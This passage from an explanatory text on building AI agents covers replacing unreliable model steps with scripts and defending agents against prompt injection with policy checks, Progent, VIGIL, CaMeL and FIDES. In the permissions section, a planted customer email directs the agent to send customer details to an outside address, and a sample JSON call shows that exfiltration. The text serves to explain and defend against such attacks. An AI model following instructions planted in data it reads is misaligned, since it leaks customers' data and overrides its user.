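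In *Building an internal agent*, Will Larson describes a problem that a saved script can fix. At his company, Imprint, engineers post pull requests (proposed code changes) in a Slack channel for colleagues to review. Larson wanted to mark the ones that no longer needed a review, so he gave an agent a short prompt and the necessary tools. The agent was to read the last ten messages, look up each pull request on GitHub and add a "merged" emoji if it had been merged or closed.

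The agent usually worked well, but it sometimes put its emoji on pull requests that hadn't been merged, and then nobody reviewed them. No schema could have caught these semantic errors, and even occasional ones defeated the tool's purpose because people could no longer trust the emoji.

Larson's team changed the harness so that a Python script could take over from the model. The script has the same tools and can still call a model for a step that needs one, and an engineer reviews it before use. The decision about the emoji becomes an `if` statement that reads the status from GitHub. Larson says the approach has worked very well for his team's complex workflows, but he gives no error rates from before or after the change. The team still starts every workflow with a prompt and rewrites it as a script only if it proves too unreliable or slow. Claude Code can almost always do this in one attempt.

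The script can't interpret messages as a model can. If an engineer writes "this replaces yesterday's change" without a link, a model might work out which pull request is meant, but a script that looks for links will skip the message. Someone also has to update the script when the team's habits change.

Qiu, Ye and colleagues (2025), in *Blueprint First, Model Second*, build whole agents this way at Alibaba. An expert writes the procedure as code, and the code calls the model only at chosen points for limited jobs, such as interpreting an error log. When a Java server runs out of memory, for example, the code reads the memory statistics and uses a fixed threshold to choose the next diagnostic step. The model explains the findings, and its explanations can still vary from run to run, but it never chooses the next step.

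TravelPlanner is a benchmark of trip planning under many rules, such as not visiting the same restaurant twice. With Claude Sonnet 4, a 2025 model, the design produced acceptable plans for 35.56% of the benchmark's tasks. ATLAS, a system of several cooperating agents that states such rules in prompts, reached 18.00% with the same model. Rule violations fell from 275 to 11, largely because a line of code that rejects a repeated restaurant does so every time it runs. But almost two thirds of the plans still failed, and these figures don't measure how often the same request leads to the same plan.

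But the developer has to know the procedure in advance. Qiu and colleagues recommend the design for work with well-defined steps and many constraints. The code has no branch for a fault that the expert didn't foresee, whereas an ordinary agent could at least investigate it.

In *From Research Question to Scientific Workflow*, Balis, Orzechowski and colleagues (2026) give the model an even smaller role. Their system turns a geneticist's question into a computing job. The model fills in one schema-bound record, called an intent, with the populations, chromosomes and regions to study. Ordinary code then builds the job from the intent, the size of the data and the number of available processors, so the same intent always produces the same job on the same cluster.

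All the variation now comes from the step that interprets the question. On 150 test questions, Claude Opus 4.6 got the whole intent right 44% of the time on its own and 83% with reference documents written by experts. With the documents, it was always right on questions that used the official codes or common names for populations, but it averaged about 65% on questions that left out details or contained invalid terms. A wrong intent produces the same wrong job every time, so the system shows the scientist its plan before it runs anything.

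This design works because the possible requests are few enough to list. The test covered 26 population codes, 24 chromosomes and 8 named regions. Adding a region only requires editing a table, but adding a new kind of analysis would require new code. In return, the scientist has only one short record to check.

The shop could handle its late-parcel refunds the same way. After a developer has reviewed the script from the manager's first batch, the shop can save it as a tool called `refund_late_orders`, whose only argument is a list of order numbers. The validator checks the list, and the saved code identifies the late parcels and calculates a fifth of each price. The model can still leave an order off the list, but it can no longer change the formula. If the manager later wants to refund half the price to customers whose parcels have been late twice, a developer has to change the tool first.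 An agent with `get_order` and `issue_refund` could try it straight away, but its calls might vary from run to run because the model chooses each one afresh.

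## Valid calls that should not be allowed: permissions, policies and data flow

Suppose the shop's manager asks the agent to read the day's customer emails and send back a summary. One email contains text aimed at the agent, telling it to send customers' details to an outside address. This is *prompt injection*, the practice of planting text in data an agent reads to make the agent follow someone else's instructions. If the model obeys, the run may contain these two calls to `send_email`:

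```json
{ "to": "manager@shop.example", "subject": "Today's emails",
  "body": "Nine customers wrote to us today ..." }

{ "to": "someone@elsewhere.example", "subject": "Details",
  "body": "Order A-1042 ..." }
```

The tool's schema requires three strings, and both calls supply them. Both would also pass a rule that `to` must be a well-formed email address. Strict mode makes no difference, because the model has followed the required format. If the manager had asked for the details to be sent to that outside address, the second call would be correct.

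A developer can measure how often mistakes such as the $64.00 refund happen. But an attacker looks for whatever the checks miss and can try again after failing, so a low error rate on ordinary tasks is weak evidence that the system will withstand attacks.

### Tool lists, policy checks and data-flow tracking

Developers can limit the agent at three points before the second email goes out.

| Protection | What it limits | In the email example |
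|---|---|---|
| Short tool list | Which tools the agent can call at all | An agent that only sorts emails has no `send_email` |
| Policy check | Which arguments a tool accepts in the present context | For this request, `to` must be the manager's address |
| Data-flow tracking | Where data from each source may go | Text from a customer's email can't choose the recipient |

A short tool list follows the principle of *least privilege*, giving a program only the permissions its task needs. It adds almost no overhead, and injected text can't make the agent use a tool that isn't on the list. But *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) separates the tools an agent can call from the actions its user has authorised, and a tool list controls only the first. The manager's request needs `send_email`, so that tool has to stay on the list.

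A *policy check* is a rule, applied before execution, that determines whether a valid call is permitted in the current context. It can allow the tool but restrict the recipient, which works when the request makes the right recipient clear. But if the manager asks the agent to send an invoice to every customer who wanted one, the rule has to permit every customer's address. A malicious customer could then try to obtain somebody else's invoice, and both the tool and the recipient would be permitted. To block that call, the software has to track whose invoice it is.

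### The AgentDojo benchmark

Most of the measurements below come from AgentDojo, a 2024 benchmark that simulates an office workspace, a travel service, a bank and the messaging service Slack. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, count 97 user tasks and 36 attacker goals in it. In a security test, the agent attempts each user task once for every attacker goal in the same environment, with the attacker's instructions placed in data that a tool returns. Programs then check separately whether the agent achieved the user's goal and whether it achieved the attacker's.

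The benchmark includes a version of the short tool list, in which a model reads the user's request before the run starts and removes every tool that the task doesn't seem to need. With GPT-4o, a 2024 model, Costa and colleagues counted 152 successful attacks on an ordinary agent and 20 on one with the filtered list. A good list therefore prevents most of these attacks, but it can't stop an attack that uses a tool the user's task also needs.

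### Progent: a rule for each call

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, check the arguments as well. A Progent rule either allows or forbids a tool, states conditions on its arguments, and says what to do if it blocks a call. For the manager's request, the rule might be:

```
allow send_email when { to == "manager@shop.example" },
  fallback: return an error message
```

Progent checks every call the agent makes. It applies rules that forbid calls before rules that allow them, and blocks any call that matches no rule. When it blocks a call, it can end the run, ask the user or, by default, return a message that explains the refusal and repeats the user's task. The agent can then drop the outside email and still send the summary. Shi and colleagues wrote the rules in JSON Schema, so a policy is in effect a second, narrower schema that applies to one task.

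Nobody can write such rules by hand for every request, so a language model drafts them from the user's message before the agent reads anything else. Some tasks, such as working through a to-do list in an email, need permissions that become clear only later. The model therefore proposes changes to the rules as results arrive, and injected text in those results could influence the changes.

Progent deals with this by comparing the old and new rules. Let `A(P)` be the set of calls that policy `P` allows. A *solver*, a program that decides whether logical conditions can hold together, tests whether

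```
A(P_new) ⊆ A(P_old)
```

A new policy that only removes permissions takes effect at once. Somebody has to approve a policy that would allow at least one new call. In the tests, 6% of updates needed approval.

With GPT-4o on AgentDojo, Progent cut the share of successful attacks from 39.9% to 1.0% and left the completion of ordinary tasks about the same. In that test, Shi and colleagues set Progent to approve every expansion of the agent's permissions automatically, to imitate a careless user. When a person reviewed the rules instead, no attack succeeded. When the rules were drafted from the request alone and never updated, 2.5% of attacks succeeded. Claude Sonnet 4, from 2025, was far more resistant even without Progent, with 6.8% of attacks succeeding, and Progent reduced that to 0.5%.

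The check can't stop an attack that stays within the task's permissions. If injected text makes the agent leave a complaint out of the summary, the email still goes to the manager and matches the rule. Progent also doesn't check the agent's text answers, because they aren't tool calls.

### VIGIL: rules about the whole run

Some rules depend on what happened earlier. The shop might want the agent to look up an order before refunding it. AgentSpec, an earlier system, attaches each rule to a trigger, such as a proposed refund, and evaluates the rule when the agent proposes that action. According to Li, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *VIGIL*, such a check can't trace which order the agent looked up several steps ago. VIGIL keeps a record of the run and states rules over it:

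```
prec( issue_refund with order_id = x,
      get_order    with order_id = x )
```

This rule allows a refund for order `x` only after a lookup of the same order. When the agent proposes a refund, VIGIL combines the record with the rule and uses a solver to check whether they contradict each other. If they do, VIGIL blocks the refund and identifies the call at fault. The harness can then stop the run, ask the user or return to an earlier checkpoint. Other rules forbid an action or require something to follow it. VIGIL can check a requirement such as "email the customer after every refund" only when the run ends, because the agent may still send the email before then.

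Li and colleagues tested VIGIL on 152 recorded runs in which agents used *skills*, packages of instructions and code for a particular kind of work. In 72 of the runs, the agent had broken a rule in the skill's documentation.

| System | Rule-breaking runs found, of 72 | Harmless runs flagged, of 80 |
|---|---|---|
| VIGIL | 69 | 8 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 as a judge | 48 | 5 |
| Progent | 40 | 47 |
| AgentSpec | 34 | 12 |

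The test set suits VIGIL because it consists largely of violations that cannot be detected from any single call. But on recorded AgentDojo runs, all four systems found at least 95% of the violations. A developer who is mainly worried about an agent emailing a stranger may therefore only need to check each call on its own.

VIGIL's figures also measure something different from Progent's. *Who Holds the Pen?* (Li, Ma and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes checks made after the work is over, checks on the agent's claim to have finished, and checks during execution. Only a check during execution can stop an email from being sent. VIGIL is designed to run during execution, but in this experiment it was applied to finished runs. The results show how often VIGIL would flag a problem, but not how many tasks an agent would still complete after being blocked. Progent's tests used live agents and did measure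 task completion after blocking.

An agent's claim to have finished is still worth checking for other reasons. Across seven models, agents claimed completion 28.7 to 37.9 percentage points more often than the benchmark's tests confirmed it.

### CaMeL: a program written before the agent reads anything

Debenedetti and colleagues proposed CaMeL in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). Suppose the manager asks the agent to take the delivery address from Priya's latest email and send it to the courier. With CaMeL, the work goes roughly like this:

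1. A planning model receives the manager's request and the tool descriptions, but none of the emails. It writes a short program in a restricted form of Python.

```python
email = get_latest_email(sender="priya@customer.example")
address = ask_reader("Extract the delivery address.", email.body)
send_email(to="dispatch@courier.example",
           subject="New delivery address", body=address)
```

2. An interpreter runs the program and labels every value with its origin. The courier's address comes from the manager, and `email.body` comes from Priya.
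3. `ask_reader` passes the email to a second model, which has no tools and can only return a value. That value, `address`, inherits the email's label.
4. Before `send_email` runs, the interpreter checks a policy against the labels. The policy might require that the recipient come from the manager's request and that the recipient be allowed to read everything in the body.
5. If the check passes, the email goes out.

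Injected text in Priya's email never reaches the planning model, and the program already exists when the interpreter opens the email. The injected text therefore can't add a call or change the recipient, but it may still cause the second model to return a false address, which the courier would then receive.

*AutoDojo* (2026) retested CaMeL and other defences on AgentDojo tasks, using newer models and both the original attacks and newly generated ones. Up to 50.4% of the attacks succeeded against Gemini 2.5 Flash with no defence, while attacks on agents protected by CaMeL rarely succeeded.

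The protection can also stop an agent from completing legitimate tasks. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found that turning on CaMeL's policy checks halved the share of AgentDojo's banking tasks it completed. One likely reason is that when a customer asks the agent to pay a bill in a file, the account number comes from that file, so a rule against untrusted recipients blocks a payment the customer wants.

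CaMeL's planner also needs a description of what each tool returns before it sees any result. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) reports that AgentDojo's tool descriptions lacked this information, so the researchers had to add it for every tool. The same information was missing in Rai's tests of ordinary scripts. For a fixed set of tools, it only has to be added once. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) points out that work on a screen is harder to plan in advance, because the plan needs a separate branch for every state the screen might be in.

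Garby and colleagues show that CaMeL's labels can also miss information that a program reveals through a branch it doesn't take, or through whether a policy stopped an earlier attempt. They designed a small language in which every step carries labels forward. A machine-checked proof shows that programs in this language can't leak secrets, except for what an outsider learns from whether the program finishes. Their agent, with checks always on, completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did with its checks off, and it withstood all but two of 1,296 attacked runs. The banking comparison covers only one of four environments, but it suggests that CaMeL could avoid much of its loss in completed tasks.

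### Whether code is the less secure choice

It is reasonable to assume that an agent that writes free-form code is riskier than one that fills in typed calls, since Felendler and colleagues found that code exposes an agent to more kinds of attack. But typed calls don't make an agent safe by themselves. Hundreds of attacks succeeded against the undefended agents in AgentDojo, which used typed tools, while CaMeL's agents write programs and are much harder to hijack.

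Part of the reason is that a program written before the agent reads any outside data can't contain an attacker's instructions, whereas a script that the model writes after reading the emails can. Code also records where data goes. In CaMeL's program, anyone can see that `address` comes from the email and ends up in the body. When an ordinary agent reads the email and then writes a call, the address passes through the model, so software can't determine which parts of the call the email influenced.

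The programming language also matters. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) uses the example of an agent that compiles a bibliography and must not invent entries. With an unrestricted Python interpreter, the agent can write anything to the bibliography file. A single tool that fetches an entry and saves it is safe, but the agent can do little else with it. In the paper's design, the agent writes Haskell, a language with strict types, and the type checker rejects any program that writes to the file other than by fetching and saving an entry. The agent can otherwise combine its tools freely.

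So code can be the safer choice when the planner works from trusted text, the language is small and the software checks each call. Few coding agents in everyday use meet all three conditions.

### Microsoft's labels for ordinary tool calls

Costa and colleagues, at Microsoft, get a similar effect without code. Their system, FIDES, applies *information-flow control*, an older technique that labels data and restricts where each label may go. One label records whether data is trusted. Anything derived from both trusted and untrusted data counts as untrusted. Another lists who may read the data, and combined data keeps only the readers that its sources share:

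```
Priya's invoice:   {shop, Priya}
Sam's invoice:     {shop, Sam}
Both in one file:  {shop, Priya} ∩ {shop, Sam} = {shop}
```

If Sam's email leads the agent to try to send him Priya's invoice, the call fails because Sam isn't one of the invoice's permitted readers. A second rule allows consequential actions, such as payments, only if nothing untrusted influenced the decision to take them.

The second rule severely limits an ordinary agent, because everything the model writes after reading one customer's email counts as untrusted. FIDES therefore stores untrusted text in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to a tool without reading the text, or have a second model with no tools summarise it. The model can also read the text itself, but it can't take consequential actions afterwards.

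The table shows the share of ordinary tasks that GPT-4o completed when nobody was attacking.

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no policies | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary, with policies | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, with policies | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

With the policies on, no attack achieved anything the rules prohibited. But the ordinary agent completed nearly four fifths fewer Slack tasks, and FIDES recovered only some of them. Some of the loss occurred because GPT-4o used variables poorly. With o1, an early reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks, compared with 41% with GPT-4o. The rest occurred because the policy blocked actions it was meant to block, for example when a banking task told the agent to follow instructions in a file.

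The clean security result is partly due to the labels. AgentDojo doesn't label data as trusted or untrusted, so Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. A shop would have to decide in advance which fields an attacker could reach, and an attack could get through any field it wrongly trusted.

FIDES also uses schemas for security. Constrained decoding can limit the second model's answer to "yes" or "no", and a policy may treat so small an answer as safe to read. Zhou and Zhang caution that even one word can cause harm if the question is whether a confidential draft has approval for release. A schema limits how much an attacker can say, but someone still has to decide which questions the model may answer from an untrusted document.

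### Counting approvals instead of failures

In February 2026 most of the researchers behind FIDES, with two new colleagues, argued that tables like the one above treat these defences unfairly. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, point out that an agent with no defence shouldn't be making payments unsupervised in the first place. In practice a person approves its consequential calls. They therefore counted how many approvals each design needed, and how many tasks it finished with none. These are the results for o3-mini on AgentDojo:

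| Agent | Approvals across completed tasks | Tasks completed with no approval |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, a person approves every consequential call | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Ordinary, with labels and policies | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | About 17 | 59.1% |

Prudentia extends FIDES. It tells the model the policies, so the model can plan calls that comply instead of making calls that are blocked. It can also ask the user to vouch for a piece of data. If a trusted colleague emails a list of ten tasks, the user can approve the email once instead of approving ten calls.

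By this comparison, a strict policy saves work. The comparison assumes that people approve calls carefully, which, if anything, favors the ordinary agent. *L3M* (2026) cites a figure showing that users accept about 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts. People might check prompts more carefully if there were fewer of them. *APPA* (2026), a July follow-up, tries to reduce the loss further by letting a blocked agent continue in an isolated branch.

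### Writing the rules and keeping them correct

All of these systems depend on someone's rules. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent's guarantees are only as good as its policies, which people write by hand and can get wrong. Models can also make mistakes when they write the rules. In one of VIGIL's false alarms, a skill's documentation restricted *bulk* calendar changes, but the model that translated it into rules dropped the word "bulk", so VIGIL flagged an agent for moving a single meeting.

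A correct rule can also lose some of its restrictions before it reaches the system that enforces it. Zhou and Zhang describe a user who permits an agent to send one summary to Alice. The policy records this correctly, but the credential that reaches the mail service authorizes the agent to send mail without further limits. The service would accept the credential as valid and deliver to anyone. Limits can fail in a similar way when agents share work. If the shop may buy only one replacement mug but two helper agents each have permission to buy one, the shop can end up with two mugs even though each agent obeyed its own rule.

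An update can make a tool forward its input to an outside service without changing the tool's name or schema, so the old permission now covers a new disclosure. Zhou and Zhang suggest that each tool come with a description of what it reads, what it sends and to whom, and what it changes. This would give a policy more information than a list of arguments does, but tool authors would have to keep the description accurate.

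The burden of writing rules depends heavily on the agent's job. The shop's support agent has a handful of tools, and a few rules about recipients and amounts would cover most of the risks. A general office assistant connected to hundreds of tools needs many more rules, and most research on drafting rules automatically focuses on agents like this.

### When the only argument is a shell command

A shell tool undermines all three protections. Its schema accepts any command, as the one in Codex does. A short tool list does little to restrict an agent if it includes a shell, because the shell can start almost any program on the machine.

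Policy checks have to work from the text of a command, which is a poor guide to its effect. There are many ways to write the same operation, and one string can hold several commands. A policy that permits only listed commands blocks many harmless ones. All 47 of Progent's false alarms in the VIGIL test were calls that its list didn't include.

VIGIL tries to recover the missing structure by identifying the arguments of common commands and parsing Python, JavaScript and shell scripts to find which files and values they use. Without this step, it detected 63.9% of rule-breaking runs instead of 95.8%, and flagged more of the harmless ones. Even with it, VIGIL treated one agent's script as a single command. The script was supposed to encrypt a file, verify the archive and then delete the original, but it deleted the file without doing the first two steps.

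Lower-level checks can cover more of what an agent does. Zhou and Zhang list systems that inspect a browser's web requests or confine the processes behind MCP servers, and these work however the agent phrased its command. A sandbox similarly restricts access to files and the network. But these checks have less information about the purpose of an action. A web request to the payment company looks much the same whether the refund is $18.50 or $64.00, unless someone has built the checker to interpret the request's contents.

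For the shop, the simplest option is to leave out the shell, because customer support doesn't require one. A coding agent needs a shell, but the developer can keep customer records and payment keys out of its environment, and put actions such as publishing a release behind separate typed tools whose calls can be checked against a policy.
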